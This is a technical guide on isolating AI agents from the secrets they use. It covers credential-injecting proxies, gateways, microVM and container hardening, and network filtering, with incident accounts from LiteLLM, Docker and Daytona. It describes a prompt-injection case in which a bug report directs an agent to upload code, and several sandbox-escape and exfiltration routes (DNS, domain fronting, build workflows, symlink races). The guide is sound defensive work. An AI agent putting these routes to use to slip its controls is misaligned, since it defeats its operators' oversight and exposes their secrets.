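The design fails with programs that have no base URL setting. It also fits GitHub poorly, because GitHub's replies contain full web addresses, such as the address of the next page in a list of bug reports. A program that follows one of them goes to `api.github.com` instead of the gateway, so the gateway would have to rewrite those addresses. Services that use WebSockets, which are lasting two-way connections that start as web requests, work only if the gateway supports them.

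### A proxy that terminates TLS

For GitHub, Acme would rather let the agent's programs use the normal address. A forward proxy allows this. Most command-line programs read environment variables called `HTTP_PROXY` and `HTTPS_PROXY`, and if these are set, they send their traffic through the address given there. For an encrypted request, the program first asks the proxy to open a tunnel:

```
CONNECT api.github.com:443 HTTP/1.1
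```

An ordinary proxy then relays encrypted data it can't read, so it can't add a token. An intermediary that adds one has to terminate TLS, and the agent's program must accept the intermediary in GitHub's place.

Certificates normally prevent this kind of impersonation. Every computer has a list of certificate authorities, organisations that it trusts to confirm which server owns which name. Each authority has a private key for signing certificates and a public certificate that lets others check the signatures. Acme can create an authority of its own and add its public certificate to the list inside the sandbox. A request for the shop's bug reports then goes as follows:

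1. The program asks the intermediary for a tunnel to `api.github.com` and begins to set up TLS.
2. The intermediary creates a certificate for `api.github.com`, signs it with Acme's authority, and presents it.
3. The program finds Acme's authority on its list, accepts the certificate, and sends its request.
4. The intermediary decrypts the request, applies its rules, and writes the real token into the Authorization line.
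5. The intermediary opens a separate TLS connection to GitHub, checks GitHub's genuine certificate, and sends the request.
6. The reply comes back to the intermediary, which encrypts it for the program.

The check in step 5 is essential because if the intermediary skipped it, an attacker on the network could pose as GitHub and receive the token, and the program in the sandbox would not detect the attack.

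The authority's private key has to stay outside the sandbox, and each sandbox should have its own authority. Anyone with the private key can impersonate every website to every program that trusts the authority. If Acme's two teams shared one authority and its key leaked, an attacker with access to the network could pose as GitHub to both teams' agents. Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* describes a temporary authority for each sandbox, with a private key that stays in a separate process. Infisical instead keeps a permanent root key on its server and uses it to sign a seven-day certificate for each proxy, which then signs a 24-hour certificate for each hostname. An attacker who steals a proxy's key can therefore impersonate websites only until that proxy's seven-day certificate expires.

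With this design, the agent holds the authority's public certificate, which isn't secret, and at most a placeholder for the API secret. The intermediary can inspect every web request and reply that it decrypts. Most existing programs work unchanged, with several exceptions.

**Some programs ignore the proxy variables.** The `fetch` function in Node.js, a common system for running JavaScript, ignores them by default, although version 24 and later have a setting that changes this. Such a program tries to reach GitHub directly, and either it can't connect or it sends GitHub a useless placeholder instead of the secret. A transparent proxy solves this because the network redirects the traffic to it. Loganathan says LangSmith's intermediary doesn't depend on proxy variables because some programs ignore them.

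**Programs that reject the certificate.** Some programs keep their own list of authorities, so Acme has to add its certificate there too. Infisical's launcher sets six environment variables to cover common tools. Other programs use certificate pinning, which means they accept only a particular certificate or key for a service. They refuse the intermediary's certificate whatever the list contains, and a transparent proxy doesn't help.

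**Requests that the program signs.** If a program uses its secret to compute a signature, neither the secret nor its placeholder appears in the request, so the intermediary has nothing to replace. The upstream service rejects a signature made with a placeholder. Even a genuine signature becomes invalid if any part of the request it covers changes.

**WebSockets and protocols other than HTTP.** An intermediary can add a token to the request that opens a WebSocket. If the service expects the token in a later message, an intermediary that edits only headers can't supply it. Database connections and SSH don't use HTTP. In its manual, Infisical tells users to replace SSH with HTTPS and a token, which works for GitHub because Git supports both protocols.

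### Overwriting a credential or replacing a placeholder

The intermediary can attach the token in two ways. It can overwrite the Authorization header, whatever the agent put there, or it can search the request for a known placeholder and replace only that. In Docker's agent sandboxes, built-in services such as GitHub use overwriting and user-defined secrets use replacement, according to the manual, *Manage credentials*.

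Replacing placeholders and overwriting the key have different results when the agent supplies somebody else's key. Suppose a bug report from a stranger tells Acme's agent to upload the shop's code to the model provider, using a key included in the report. The provider is an approved destination because the agent needs it for every step of its work. An intermediary that only replaces placeholders finds none and forwards the request with the stranger's key, so the code goes to the stranger's account. An intermediary that overwrites the key sends the upload to Acme's account, where the stranger can't read it.

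For this protection to work, the intermediary must remove every form of credential the service accepts. Some services accept a key in either an `Authorization` or an `x-api-key` header. If the intermediary overwrites one and forwards the other, the service may act on the stranger's key.

One drawback of overwriting is that every request to GitHub receives Acme's authority, including requests that a program meant to send anonymously. Another is that if the second team's agent sent its own valid token through the same route, the intermediary would replace it with Acme's token, and GitHub would record the wrong account. Jin and colleagues are stricter and reject requests in which the agent supplies a sensitive authorisation header. Acme could combine the methods by accepting only its placeholder or an empty header, then writing the real token. A stranger's key would cause a visible error, which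 is also useful evidence of an attack.

Replacement is necessary when a service requires the secret in an unusual place. Telegram, for example, puts a bot's token in the web address. Infisical's proxy can replace placeholders in the path, the query (the part of an address after the question mark), the headers or the body, and the user chooses which of these it searches.

Searching the request body for placeholders can expose the secret. Suppose the agent includes the placeholder in a comment on a bug report. An intermediary that searches the body replaces the placeholder with the real token, and GitHub publishes the token in the comment. A rule about destinations wouldn't stop this, because the request goes to the right service and uses a permitted action. Docker's proxy avoids the problem by replacing placeholders only in named headers. Acme should do the same and search other parts of a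 request only where an API requires it, at the exact position where the secret belongs.

Encoding can also make replacement fail. When Git sends a token over HTTPS, it joins the username and token and converts the result to base64, a way of writing data with a limited set of characters. The placeholder no longer appears in its original form, so the intermediary must decode the header before searching it. Overwriting avoids this problem because the intermediary builds the whole header itself.

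A placeholder's format matters because some programs check that a key looks right before they send anything. Infisical adds that agents often refuse to attempt a call without a realistic key. Docker uses the fixed text `proxy-managed` where any value will do and a random string beginning with `sbx-cs-` for secrets that users define. A random placeholder is safer to replace because it won't turn up in ordinary text. If each sandbox has a different placeholder, one found in a public comment can also be traced to its sandbox.

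Whichever method Acme chooses, someone must check where in the request the service requires the secret. Kenney and colleagues tested a connection to FRED, an economic data service, in which the key was sent in an Authorization header. FRED required the key in the query and rejected the call, so the connection didn't work, though no secret leaked.

### A tool that the agent names

The intermediary can also offer the agent a short list of operations instead of a route to the network. Acme might define a tool called `list_issues`, and the agent would ask for it like this:

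```
list_issues(repository = "acme/shop", state = "open")
```

The intermediary checks the two values, builds the web request, adds the token, calls GitHub, and returns the list. The agent holds no placeholder and never writes a web address or a header. The intermediary can inspect the operation, its inputs and the reply. It doesn't need a certificate authority because it makes the encrypted connection to GitHub itself.

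Jin and colleagues chose this kind of design because a general proxy leaves the agent too much freedom to redirect and reshape requests. In their prototype, the agent first asks for permission to make a particular kind of request and receives a temporary handle that works only in that session. When the agent uses the handle, the intermediary checks the method, host, path, size and headers, then compares the body with a template of permitted fields. Such checks leave almost no room for misuse of `list_issues`, but a tool that accepted any method and path would in effect be a general proxy.

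The tests are evidence that this design prevents key leaks. In the web scenarios, the two comparison systems, which gave the agent the key, leaked it in every trial, and the prototype never did. The tests don't show whether the narrower operations prevent misuse, because none of the three systems ever made an unauthorised request.

This approach mainly causes problems for existing programs. `git`, GitHub's command-line tool and the scripts that an agent writes all make web requests rather than calling tools such as `list_issues`. Somebody has to build and maintain a tool for each operation. Anthropic suggests a compromise for Git, in which the agent passes commands to a tool that forwards them to a proxy outside the sandbox, and the proxy adds the credentials.

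### A signer that keeps the key

Some services accept a signature instead of a bearer credential. Acme could replace its GitHub token with an SSH key that GitHub accepts only for `acme/shop`. The private key would stay in an SSH agent on the server, and programs in the sandbox could request signatures through a socket.

When the AI agent runs `git push`, the SSH program connects to GitHub and both sides derive an identifier unique to the connection. The program sends the SSH agent a message containing this identifier and the account name. The SSH agent signs the message, and GitHub checks the signature with the public key it has on file. A copied signature is useless on any other connection. Docker's sandboxes forward the user's SSH agent by default, although Docker's newest type of add-on has to request forwarding.

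The signer can inspect very little. The message it signs doesn't contain the repository or the Git command, so the signer can't tell a harmless download from a push that overwrites the shop's history. Everything after the login travels over an encrypted connection that the signer can't read. Jin and colleagues rejected signing for this reason. Their intermediary runs the SSH command itself, after checking the remote server's key, the command and the number of arguments. This gives it far more control but breaks programs that expect a normal SSH agent.

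Amazon's cloud uses signatures for ordinary web requests. If Acme later wanted its agent to upload finished builds there, the upload would carry a signature computed with HMAC, a function that combines a key and a message into a code that nobody can produce without the key:

```
k1 = HMAC("AWS4" + secret, date)
k2 = HMAC(k1, region)
k3 = HMAC(k2, service)
k4 = HMAC(k3, "aws4_request")
signature = HMAC(k4, time, scope and hash of the request)
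```

The hash covers the method, the address, selected headers and normally the body. Amazon repeats the calculation and compares the results. The signer must never release `k4`, because whoever has it can sign any request to that service in that region without knowing the secret.

A signer that receives only the hash cannot check what it is signing. It could sign a link that acts as a bearer credential, letting anyone who has it download a private file for up to seven days. Acme should therefore send the complete request to the intermediary, which can check it, sign it and forward it. The agent's software would sign its upload using placeholder values, and the intermediary would replace that signature with a valid one. To do this for encrypted traffic, the intermediary must terminate TLS, as before.

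Ganesan's proposal also uses signing, with a separate hardware-held key for each service. The software that runs the agent takes the service's name from the live TLS connection, so the model can't request a signature for a different service. Signing addresses a weakness of the other designs, which still send a bearer credential to the upstream service. However, Ganesan hasn't built a full implementation, and services that accept only bearer credentials would still need an intermediary to handle those credentials.

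### Choosing for each secret

| Design | What the agent holds | What the intermediary can inspect | What breaks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short-lived token without an intermediary | A working token until it expires | Nothing | Services that issue only permanent keys |
| Gateway at the API's address | A local address and a placeholder | Whole requests and replies | Programs without a base URL setting, and replies with full web addresses |
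| Proxy that terminates TLS | A placeholder or nothing, and a public certificate | Whole web requests and replies | Certificate pinning, signed requests, some WebSockets, databases and SSH |
| Tool that the agent names | The tool's name and perhaps a temporary handle | The operation, its inputs and the reply | Existing programs such as `git` |
| Signer for SSH | A connection to the signer | The login message, but not the commands | Services that accept only bearer credentials |

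Acme should put the model key behind a gateway. The agent's software calls one service and has a base URL setting, so nothing has to intercept encrypted traffic. The gateway should discard any key the agent supplies. If Acme already runs an identity provider, the gateway can use it to get short-lived tokens, and Acme can delete the permanent key.

For GitHub, Acme should use a proxy that terminates TLS for `api.github.com` and `github.com`, since the agent relies on `git` and other existing programs. The proxy should refuse any credentials other than its own and write the Authorization header itself. Instead of the current GitHub token, it should hold a GitHub App's private key and use it to obtain tokens for `acme/shop` that last an hour. The agent should use Git over HTTPS, with no SSH agent in the sandbox, because an SSH agent would let it push code in requests the proxy can't read. If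 the agent only had to read and answer bug reports, two or three named tools would be enough and would give it less authority.

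## Separating the intermediary from the agent

Acme's gateway for the model key and its proxy for GitHub cannot protect their secrets if the agent can read their memory or edit their rules. The separation has to hold even when the agent runs inside its sandbox as root, the administrator account that can override every permission. Many sandboxes run the agent as root so that it can install software, and in others the agent may become root through a flaw in an installed program.

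Daytona's *Security Advisory* (2026) describes a case where this separation was missing from the sandboxes it provides for agents. When a customer connected to a sandbox with Daytona's tools, the customer's API credential stayed in the memory of a process inside the sandbox. In the standard sandbox anyone could become root without a password, so any program with a shell could read the credential and use it to reach the customer's other sandboxes. A researcher reported the flaw on April 9, 2026, and within five hours Daytona had changed its proxy to remove the credential before a request enters the sandbox. Sandboxes without root access weren't exploitable, but removing root access would have been a weaker fix because the credential would still have been in the sandbox with the agent. Daytona found no sign of theft but told customers to replace their keys, since a thief's requests would have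 looked like ordinary traffic in its logs.

### What the two sides still share

At a minimum, Acme could run the intermediary as a separate process. This achieves little if the process runs under the agent's own account, because the agent can open the same files and sockets and may be able to read the process's memory. A separate user account stops ordinary programs from doing this, but not programs running as root.

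A sidecar is a second container that runs next to the agent's. Each container has its own view of files and processes, but both use the server's kernel. In Kubernetes, a widely used system for running containers, a sidecar also shares the agent's network address, so it can't have its own egress rule. Operators sometimes merge the two containers' process lists to make debugging easier, which may let root in the agent's container read the intermediary's environment variables and files.

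The shared kernel is a weakness. In May 2026, Docker published advice on protecting containers from Copy Fail, a Linux kernel flaw, on servers not yet patched. Two kinds of sandbox reduce this exposure. gVisor intercepts system calls, the requests that programs make to the kernel, and handles most of them itself, so an attacker has to break gVisor before reaching the real kernel. A microVM is a small virtual machine with its own kernel. To escape from one, an attacker needs a flaw in the hypervisor (the software that runs virtual machines), in the devices it simulates, or in something the operator has shared with the machine.

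| Placement | Kernel | Process table | Files | Sockets |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate process, same user | Shared | Shared | Shared | Shared |
| Separate user | Shared | Shared | Shared, with permissions that root can ignore | Shared, with permissions that root can ignore |
| Sidecar container | Shared | Separate unless merged | Only mounted folders | Mounted sockets, and local ports in Kubernetes |
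| Agent in gVisor | Shared, but mostly behind gVisor | Separate | Only mounted folders | Only those passed in |
| Agent in a microVM | Separate | Separate | Only shared folders | A virtual link to the server |
| Separate host | Separate | Separate | Separate | Network connections only |

gVisor costs almost nothing for pure computation, which needs few system calls. According to Anthropic, simple system calls take about twice as long, and work that constantly opens and closes files can be 10 to 200 times slower. Installing packages and searching a large project are work of this kind, so Acme should time one of its real builds before it chooses gVisor. Firecracker, which runs microVMs, can start one in under 125 milliseconds with less than 5 MiB of extra memory. Anthropic still rates the overhead of virtual machines as high. The Firecracker figures cover only startup and Firecracker's own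 memory, and the agent's system needs its own memory on top. A separate host adds a network trip to every request and another machine to maintain.

Acme should run each team's agent in its own microVM and run the intermediary outside the microVMs, under a dedicated user account. The agent can then have root access in its microVM without gaining any rights over the intermediary. Running the intermediary on a separate host is worthwhile when it holds secrets for many customers, or when Acme can't accept the risk of a flaw in the hypervisor.

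The two secrets also need to be kept separate from each other. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) describes a design for agents on its automation service in which one container holds the tokens for the language model and another, behind a gateway, holds the GitHub token. If Acme separates its gateway and proxy in the same way, a flaw in one doesn't automatically expose the other's secret.

### A hardened container

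Some of Acme's servers may not be able to run virtual machines. A container is the fallback there, and its safety depends on how Acme starts it. This command adapts Anthropic's example:

```
docker run \
  --user 20001:20001 \
  --cap-drop ALL \
  --security-opt no-new-privileges \
  --read-only --tmpfs /tmp:rw,nosuid,size=200m \
  --mount type=volume,src=shop-work,dst=/work \
  --network none --ipc private \
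  --memory 4g --cpus 2 --pids-limit 300 \
  --mount type=bind,src=/srv/agent1/api.sock,dst=/run/api.sock \
  acme-agent
```

| Setting | What it prevents |
|---|---|
| `--user` | The agent starting as root |
| `--cap-drop ALL` | Use of root's separate powers, such as reconfiguring the network |
| `no-new-privileges` | Programs such as `sudo` giving the agent more rights |
| `--read-only` | Lasting changes to the programs installed in the container |
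| `--tmpfs` | Temporary files surviving after the container stops |
| `--mount type=volume` | Work on the code touching folders that people use on the server |
| `--network none` | Direct connections that go around the intermediary |
| `--ipc private` | Access to memory that other containers share |
| `--memory`, `--cpus`, `--pids-limit` | A runaway program starving the intermediary on the same server |

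The last mount is a socket that leads to the intermediary, and it is the agent's only way out. Programs that expect a network port need a small relay inside the container to pass their traffic to the socket. The relay holds no secret, so it doesn't matter if the agent takes it over.

Docker also applies a seccomp profile, a filter that blocks about 44 system calls by default. Acme should leave it on. The option `--privileged` removes most of these protections, and `--pid host` makes every process on the server visible inside the container, so Acme should not use either option in an agent's configuration.

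By default, user 20001 in the container is also user 20001 on the server, so the intermediary must run under a different user ID. A separate Docker setting, `--userns-remap`, maps root in the container to an unprivileged account on the server. Mounting the socket as read-only wouldn't limit what the agent can send through it. Acme should mount only that socket, or a folder that contains nothing else, because mounting all of `/var/run` would usually expose Docker's control socket too.

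These settings also prevent the agent from installing system software with `sudo`, so Acme has to build the tools into the container image beforehand. Docker's agent sandboxes avoid this limitation by giving the agent `sudo` inside a microVM and relying entirely on the hypervisor for isolation, as Docker's *Isolation layers* explains. The intermediary's container should have its own set of mounts and the same restrictions as the agent's container, except on network access.

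### Files that cross the boundary

Even if a sandbox works perfectly, the agent can leave a file for someone else to run. Developers often share a project folder with the agent, and many tools run programs that they find in such folders. Git runs scripts called hooks when someone commits or pushes code, editors can start tasks when a person opens a project, and coding agents run commands listed in their settings files. These scripts, tasks and commands run outside the sandbox with the developer's rights, and may be able to reach the intermediary's files. Docker advises treating a folder that an agent has changed like a contribution from an untrusted stranger, and checking Git hooks separately because they don't show up in the usual list of changes.

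*Names Are Not Objects* (Commey, 2026) cites seven sandbox escapes published by Pillar Security in July 2026, most of which worked in this way. Commey traces many such flaws to one error, in which a program checks a name, such as a file path, and a later step uses whatever the name then refers to. What is used can differ from what was checked because a path may be a symlink, a file that redirects to another location.

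Docker Sandboxes, which shares a project folder between the user's computer and a microVM, had two flaws of this kind. The Hacker News' *Critical Docker Sandboxes Flaw Lets Malicious Guest Code Read and Modify macOS* (2026) reports that on Macs the file-sharing program followed symlinks when it reopened a removed file. Code in the sandbox could therefore read and change any file on the computer that was accessible to the account running the virtual machine. The other flaw was in a relay that connects the sandbox to sockets in the shared folder. The relay checked a socket's path and then connected by name, so the sandbox could switch the target between the check and the connection. Docker fixed both flaws in version 0.42.0 in September 2026 and has reported no attacks.

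A separate kernel didn't help here, because the fault was in the programs that served the sandbox from outside. Such a program should open the file or socket once, check what it has opened, and use only that. Commey tested this kind of attack on a prototype that could refuse symlinks at every step of a path and stop background programs from running. The attack succeeded in all ten trials with both protections off and failed in all ten with either one on. Acme should also run the file-sharing program and the intermediary under different accounts, so that a repeat of the Mac flaw wouldn't reach the secrets.

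Docker's *CVE-2026-18171* (2026) records a different failure, in which versions 0.35.0 to 0.38.0 of Docker Sandboxes enforced read-only access to shared folders only inside the sandbox. The file-sharing server still allowed writes, so ordinary code in the sandbox could change a folder the operator believed was protected. The side the agent doesn't control has to enforce the restriction. If the agent needs to know which services it may use, Acme should give it a copy of the rules, because a flaw like this would let it edit a shared original.

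Acme's agent doesn't need a shared folder, because it can download `acme/shop` from GitHub through the proxy, work on its own copy, and push the result to a branch for review. Docker also offers a clone mode, in which the agent works on a private copy of a folder on the user's machine. The agent can't change the original in this mode, but it can still read the whole folder, including any `.env` file.

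Pushing an agent's work to a branch still gives the agent one way to reach secrets. *Tracekit Box* (2026) notes that the work an agent hands back can change the workflows that a build server runs on the next push. If Acme's build server holds secrets, the agent could obtain them by changing the code that runs there, without attacking the intermediary. GitHub has a separate permission for editing workflow files, which Acme should withhold from its app. But existing workflows also run the project's own build scripts, which the agent can change, so Acme must keep secrets out of any build of an unreviewed branch.

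### Sockets, orchestrators and administration

Docker's control socket lets anyone who can reach it start containers, including ones that mount any folder on the server. An agent with access to this socket can read the intermediary's files, however well Acme has hardened the agent's container. In Docker's sandboxes, each microVM has a private copy of Docker, so the agent can build and run containers without using the server's copy. GitHub's diagram of its design shows a link between the gateway in front of the GitHub token and the server's Docker socket. The agent can't use that socket directly, but an attacker who took over the gateway probably could.

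Leaving the socket out of the configuration isn't always enough. In August 2025 Docker fixed a flaw in Docker Desktop that let a malicious container reach the control interface even when nobody had mounted the socket. Acme should therefore try to reach the interface from inside the sandbox, and check for a forwarded SSH agent the same way.

Orchestrators such as Kubernetes start containers and supply them with their secrets, so access to the orchestrator can give access to the secrets. By default, Kubernetes puts an access token in every container. If the token's account can read stored secrets, the agent can request the intermediary's secrets. Permission to create containers is nearly as dangerous, because the agent could start one with the secrets attached. Acme should turn off the automatic token for sandboxes, give the sandbox's account no permissions, and run the intermediary in a separate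 namespace, the unit Kubernetes uses to divide permissions.

Agents also reach programs outside the sandbox through tools. Docker's *Security model* says that local MCP servers run on the user's computer with the computer's permissions, and advises users to treat them as trusted. It also describes a shared store of agent skills. If an operator makes the store writable, one sandbox can change instructions or scripts that another will use, so agents from two teams that share the store would effectively be in one sandbox.

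The intermediary's administration interface needs a separate socket that nothing in a sandbox can open. Putting the interface behind a password on the port the agent uses is weaker, because one mistake in the password check gives the agent control. The interface should let staff replace a secret but never display it. Rules and program files should belong to an administrator's account, and the intermediary should only be able to read them. An attacker who tricks the intermediary into writing a file then can't use it to add a rule.

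### When attackers take over the gateway

LiteLLM, the gateway whose packages attackers poisoned in March 2026, was compromised again in October. *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release* (Jensen and Wang, 2026) traces the second compromise to a file that the company published by mistake on May 27. The file contained the master key to LiteLLM's internal platform for running agents. Staff removed the file and noted that the key needed revoking, but nobody revoked it. On October 10 an attacker used the key to enter the platform and took the GitHub token stored there for the agents.

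That token belonged to an owner of the company's GitHub organisation, and nobody had restricted its permissions. The attacker used it to run build jobs that collected more secrets, including the tokens of two engineers. On October 21 the attacker switched off the protections on the release project and published a malicious version of the gateway, using one stolen identity to request the release and another to approve it.

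Cornelißen (2026), in *LiteLLM 1.107.0 war ein Credential-Stealer*, reports that the malware took model providers' keys from the gateway's database. It ran whenever any Python program started on the machine, even one that didn't use LiteLLM. The package was available for under two hours, and container images tagged `latest` were also infected. According to Martin (2026), in *Popular AI tool LiteLLM says unrevoked key allowed hackers to target users*, the security company Wiz counted about 49,000 downloads, and the attacker was trying out stolen Amazon credentials within four and a half hours of the upload.

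Checking the publisher's signature would not have helped, because LiteLLM's own release system had built and signed the malicious version. Acme would have been safe if it had pinned the exact version and checksum of its gateway and waited a few days before each routine upgrade. The platform that held the GitHub token needed one limited to the repositories where its agents worked.

Delaying an upgrade is dangerous when it repairs a known flaw. OSV's *CVE-2026-42208*, an entry in a public database of software flaws, describes how the LiteLLM gateway checked a caller's key by inserting it into the text of a database query. A caller with no valid key could therefore make the database run other commands and reach the credentials the gateway managed. Attackers were exploiting the flaw within 36 hours of its disclosure, according to The Hacker News' *LiteLLM CVE-2026-42208 SQL Injection Exploited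 within 36 Hours of Disclosure* (2026). Acme should therefore install security repairs as soon as someone has reviewed them and delay only other upgrades. It should also store the records of permitted callers apart from the upstream secrets, and give the component that checks callers no access to those secrets.

### Keeping the intermediary small

Every feature and outside package in the intermediary adds code that could expose its secrets. In May 2026 attackers published a malicious version of the official Python package for the model provider Mistral. LiteLLM was unaffected because it sends Mistral ordinary web requests and doesn't install the package. Acme's gateway forwards requests to one address, so it needs no web dashboard, plug-in system or database.

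Commey's prototype is a small program that controls an agent's access to files, programs and the network. It has 3,164 lines of trusted code, not counting outside packages, and handles a request in a median of 4.0 milliseconds. Of 74 attacks Commey wrote for it, 2 succeeded, compared with 56 against an ordinary command sandbox combined with a list of permitted commands. The prototype also broke three of seven normal workflows, including one that set up a Python environment. Small programs still contain errors, and Commey found eight in this one during development. Seven of them were the confusion of names and objects that the prototype was meant to prevent.

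The intermediary should never run code that the agent has chosen, including plug-ins, scripts, and programs that the intermediary looks up in the agent's folder. Running Git in a repository the agent controls is a common mistake, because the repository's configuration can make Git run other programs. If the intermediary must work on the agent's files, it should do so in a separate sandbox that has no secrets.

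Acme can also move the GitHub App's private key from the proxy, which has to decode whatever web traffic the agent sends, to a much smaller program that supplies the hourly tokens. An attacker who takes over the proxy then can't keep creating tokens after Acme shuts the attacker out.

### Storing, caching and replacing secrets

The intermediary must prove its identity to get its secrets. On a cloud platform, it can use a signed identity that the platform provides, as in the token exchanges that model providers offer. On Acme's own server, a file that only the intermediary's account can read is enough, provided the disk is encrypted and backups exclude the file. Docker's sandboxes keep keys in the operating system's keychain, according to Collabnix, a community site for Docker users. A keychain protects keys if the disk is stolen, but it often releases them to any program in the same login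 session, so the intermediary still needs its own account. Whatever store Acme uses should let the gateway read only the model key, and let the program that issues GitHub tokens read only the app's private key.

Environment variables are a poor place for a secret, even in the intermediary. In July 2025 Docker fixed a flaw that had copied sensitive variables into Docker Desktop's diagnostic logs. Reading the secret from a file or directly from the store avoids this kind of leak. Acme should also stop the operating system from saving the intermediary's memory to disk, which it may do when a program crashes or memory runs short.

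The intermediary should keep each secret in memory for a limited time. If it fetched the secret again for every request, the store would become a point of failure, and if it kept the secret indefinitely, it would never pick up a replacement. LiteLLM had outages in April 2026 because its gateway froze for 30 to 120 seconds while trying to restore a lost database connection, and Kubernetes killed it for not answering health checks. The intermediary should fetch secrets in the background and keep using the last valid copy during a short failure. When that copy reaches its time limit, the intermediary should refuse requests and report an error, and it must never fall back to a secret that grants broader access.

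Planned replacement works best with a period in which both secrets are valid:

1. Acme creates a new secret at the upstream service and leaves the old one working.
2. It puts the new secret in the store and waits until every copy of the intermediary has loaded it.
3. It checks that requests with the new secret succeed.
4. It revokes the old secret at the upstream service.
5. It sends a test request with the old secret and confirms that the service refuses it.

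If the intermediary keeps secrets for ten minutes, the wait in step 2 must last at least ten minutes. When Acme suspects theft, it should revoke the old secret first and accept the interruption. For the GitHub App, it must revoke the current one-hour tokens as well as the private key, because the tokens may still work after the key is deleted. Step 5 takes a few seconds, and LiteLLM could have used it in May to discover that its master key still worked.

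## Limiting the network on both sides

A microVM stops Acme's agent from reading the server's files, but it doesn't limit where the agent can connect. An agent with an open network connection can send the shop's code to any server on the internet, or use an old login it has found to call GitHub without the intermediary. Acme therefore needs two network rules:

- The sandbox can reach only the intermediary and whatever else Acme has expressly allowed.
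- The intermediary can reach only its named upstream services and its secret store.

The rule for the intermediary is easy to forget because Acme trusts the intermediary. But the malicious LiteLLM release took providers' keys from inside the gateway. Malware of that kind has to send the keys somewhere, and it has few places to send them if the gateway can connect only to its model provider. Neither rule controls what an agent does at an approved destination, such as posting private code on GitHub.

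### What each kind of filter can see

The strictest way to confine the sandbox is to give it no network interface except loopback, which connects programs on the same machine. Any attempt to connect elsewhere then fails in the kernel. The only way out is the socket and relay in the hardened container, or the equivalent virtual link from a microVM, so Acme doesn't have to anticipate every protocol an agent might try.

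A firewall that filters by address reads the source, destination, protocol and port of each packet. It works for databases and SSH as well as web traffic. It suits a fixed destination such as the intermediary better than GitHub, because large online services change their addresses and often share them with unrelated sites. Tuttle (2026), in *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox*, recommends address rules for private networks and fixed infrastructure, and hostname rules for services like GitHub.

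A firewall can filter TLS connections by hostname without decrypting them, because the program sends the site's name unencrypted at the start. The field that carries the name, called Server Name Indication (SNI), lets a server that hosts many sites choose which certificate to present. The firewall checks the name against an allowlist before passing on the rest of the connection. Vercel, a hosting company that sells sandboxes for agents, filters ordinary allowed domains this way.

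A program can name an approved site in the SNI field and a different one in the encrypted request's `Host` line, a technique called domain fronting. A server shared by many sites may use the `Host` line to choose which one answers. According to Vercel's *Sandbox firewall*, many providers reject such mismatches, but the firewall doesn't prevent them by default. The filter therefore guarantees only that the connection went to a server that handles the approved name. Vercel advises customers to approve narrow hostnames whose servers host nothing else. Docker (2026) added a warning to its policy tool that blocking by hostname has limits when an allowed site and a blocked site share an address.

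An intermediary that terminates TLS can read the `Host` line and either refuse the request if it doesn't match the approved name or overwrite the line with that name. Acme's proxy already decrypts traffic to GitHub, so it can do this without decrypting anything more. Vercel's firewall decrypts only traffic to domains that have rules about individual requests, and those rules are easy to misread. A rule that adds a token to requests under one path still lets requests to other paths through without the token. To block them, the customer has to add a final rule that rejects everything else.

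Combining address and hostname filters can also leave gaps. On Vercel, the two kinds of rule apply independently, so traffic to any address in an allowed range bypasses both the hostname filter and the part of the firewall that attaches credentials.

### Why proxy variables are not a boundary

Programs can ignore the `HTTP_PROXY` and `HTTPS_PROXY` variables. Code in the sandbox can delete them and connect directly, or add a site to `NO_PROXY`, which lists sites to reach without the proxy.

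The sandbox from the software company Union.ai has an allowlist that works through proxy variables. *Networking*, a page in the company's manual, describes the list as a guardrail for honest clients that won't contain hostile code. For untrusted code, the page recommends turning off the network completely and copying in the data beforehand.

Acme should still set the variables so that ordinary programs find the intermediary, but it should rely on the missing network interface, or a firewall outside the sandbox, to enforce the network limit.

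### Traffic that needs its own rules

**DNS.** Before a program connects to `api.github.com`, it normally sends a query to a DNS resolver to get the site's address. If the resolver has no stored answer, it forwards the query until it reaches a server that the domain's owner controls. The name in the query can contain data, so a sandbox that can't open any web connections can still send information to the owner of a domain.

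Docker's *CVE-2026-12039* (2026) records a failure of this kind. Docker's sandboxes checked web traffic against an allowlist, but their resolver forwarded every DNS lookup without checking the list. Sophie Lemos, an outside researcher, found the flaw, which had been present since version 0.13.0. Docker fixed it in 0.33.0, and its resolver now applies the same policy as the proxy. By contrast, VPNCentral's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore sandbox bypass allows covert DNS C2 and data exfiltration* reports that Amazon withdrew its first fix for its Bedrock AgentCore sandboxes and changed the documentation to explain that the sandbox allows DNS.

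Acme's sandbox can do without DNS if its programs use a forward proxy, because they give the proxy a hostname and the proxy looks up the address. With a transparent proxy, programs have to look up the address themselves before they connect, so Acme would need a resolver that answers only for approved names. Acme also shouldn't assume that a tight list of allowed addresses restricts DNS lookups. On Vercel, a policy that allows only private addresses and lists no domains still lets the sandbox look up any name.

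**ICMP** is the protocol networks use for error reports and `ping`. It has no ports, so rules written for TCP and UDP don't cover it, and its packets can carry data. Docker's *CVE-2026-12539* (2026) describes how Docker blocked ICMP when it created a sandbox's network, but didn't reapply the block when its background program restarted and rebuilt the network from disk. A sandbox that survived the restart could therefore send ICMP to any host, and tests of only new sandboxes would have missed this. Docker found the flaw itself and also fixed it in version 0.33.0.

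The newest version of HTTP runs over UDP, so a filter that inspects only TCP does not catch it. Docker blocks outbound UDP by default.

Many servers have both an IPv4 address and one in the newer system, IPv6. Older Linux firewall tools keep separate rules for each, so Acme could block a destination over one and leave it open over the other.

**Private address ranges.** Company networks use ranges such as `10.0.0.0/8`, and internal systems often trust any caller who can reach them. A rule that allows every address on port 443 also allows connections to these systems. Checking the hostname doesn't solve this, because a domain's owner can point it at a private address. An earlier version of Docker's sandboxes checked the address a hostname resolved to against a list of blocked ranges.

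**Cloud metadata endpoints.** On Amazon's, Google's and Microsoft's clouds, a rented server gets its temporary credentials from the fixed address `169.254.169.254`. Blocking only that address isn't enough. Union.ai's ready-made blocklist also covers the rest of its address range, Google's hostname for the service, and Amazon's IPv6 endpoint. On a cloud server, the intermediary may need the metadata endpoint to prove its own identity. If it does, Acme would have to let the intermediary use the endpoint but refuse any agent's request to forward traffic there.

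### When the policy and the connection disagree

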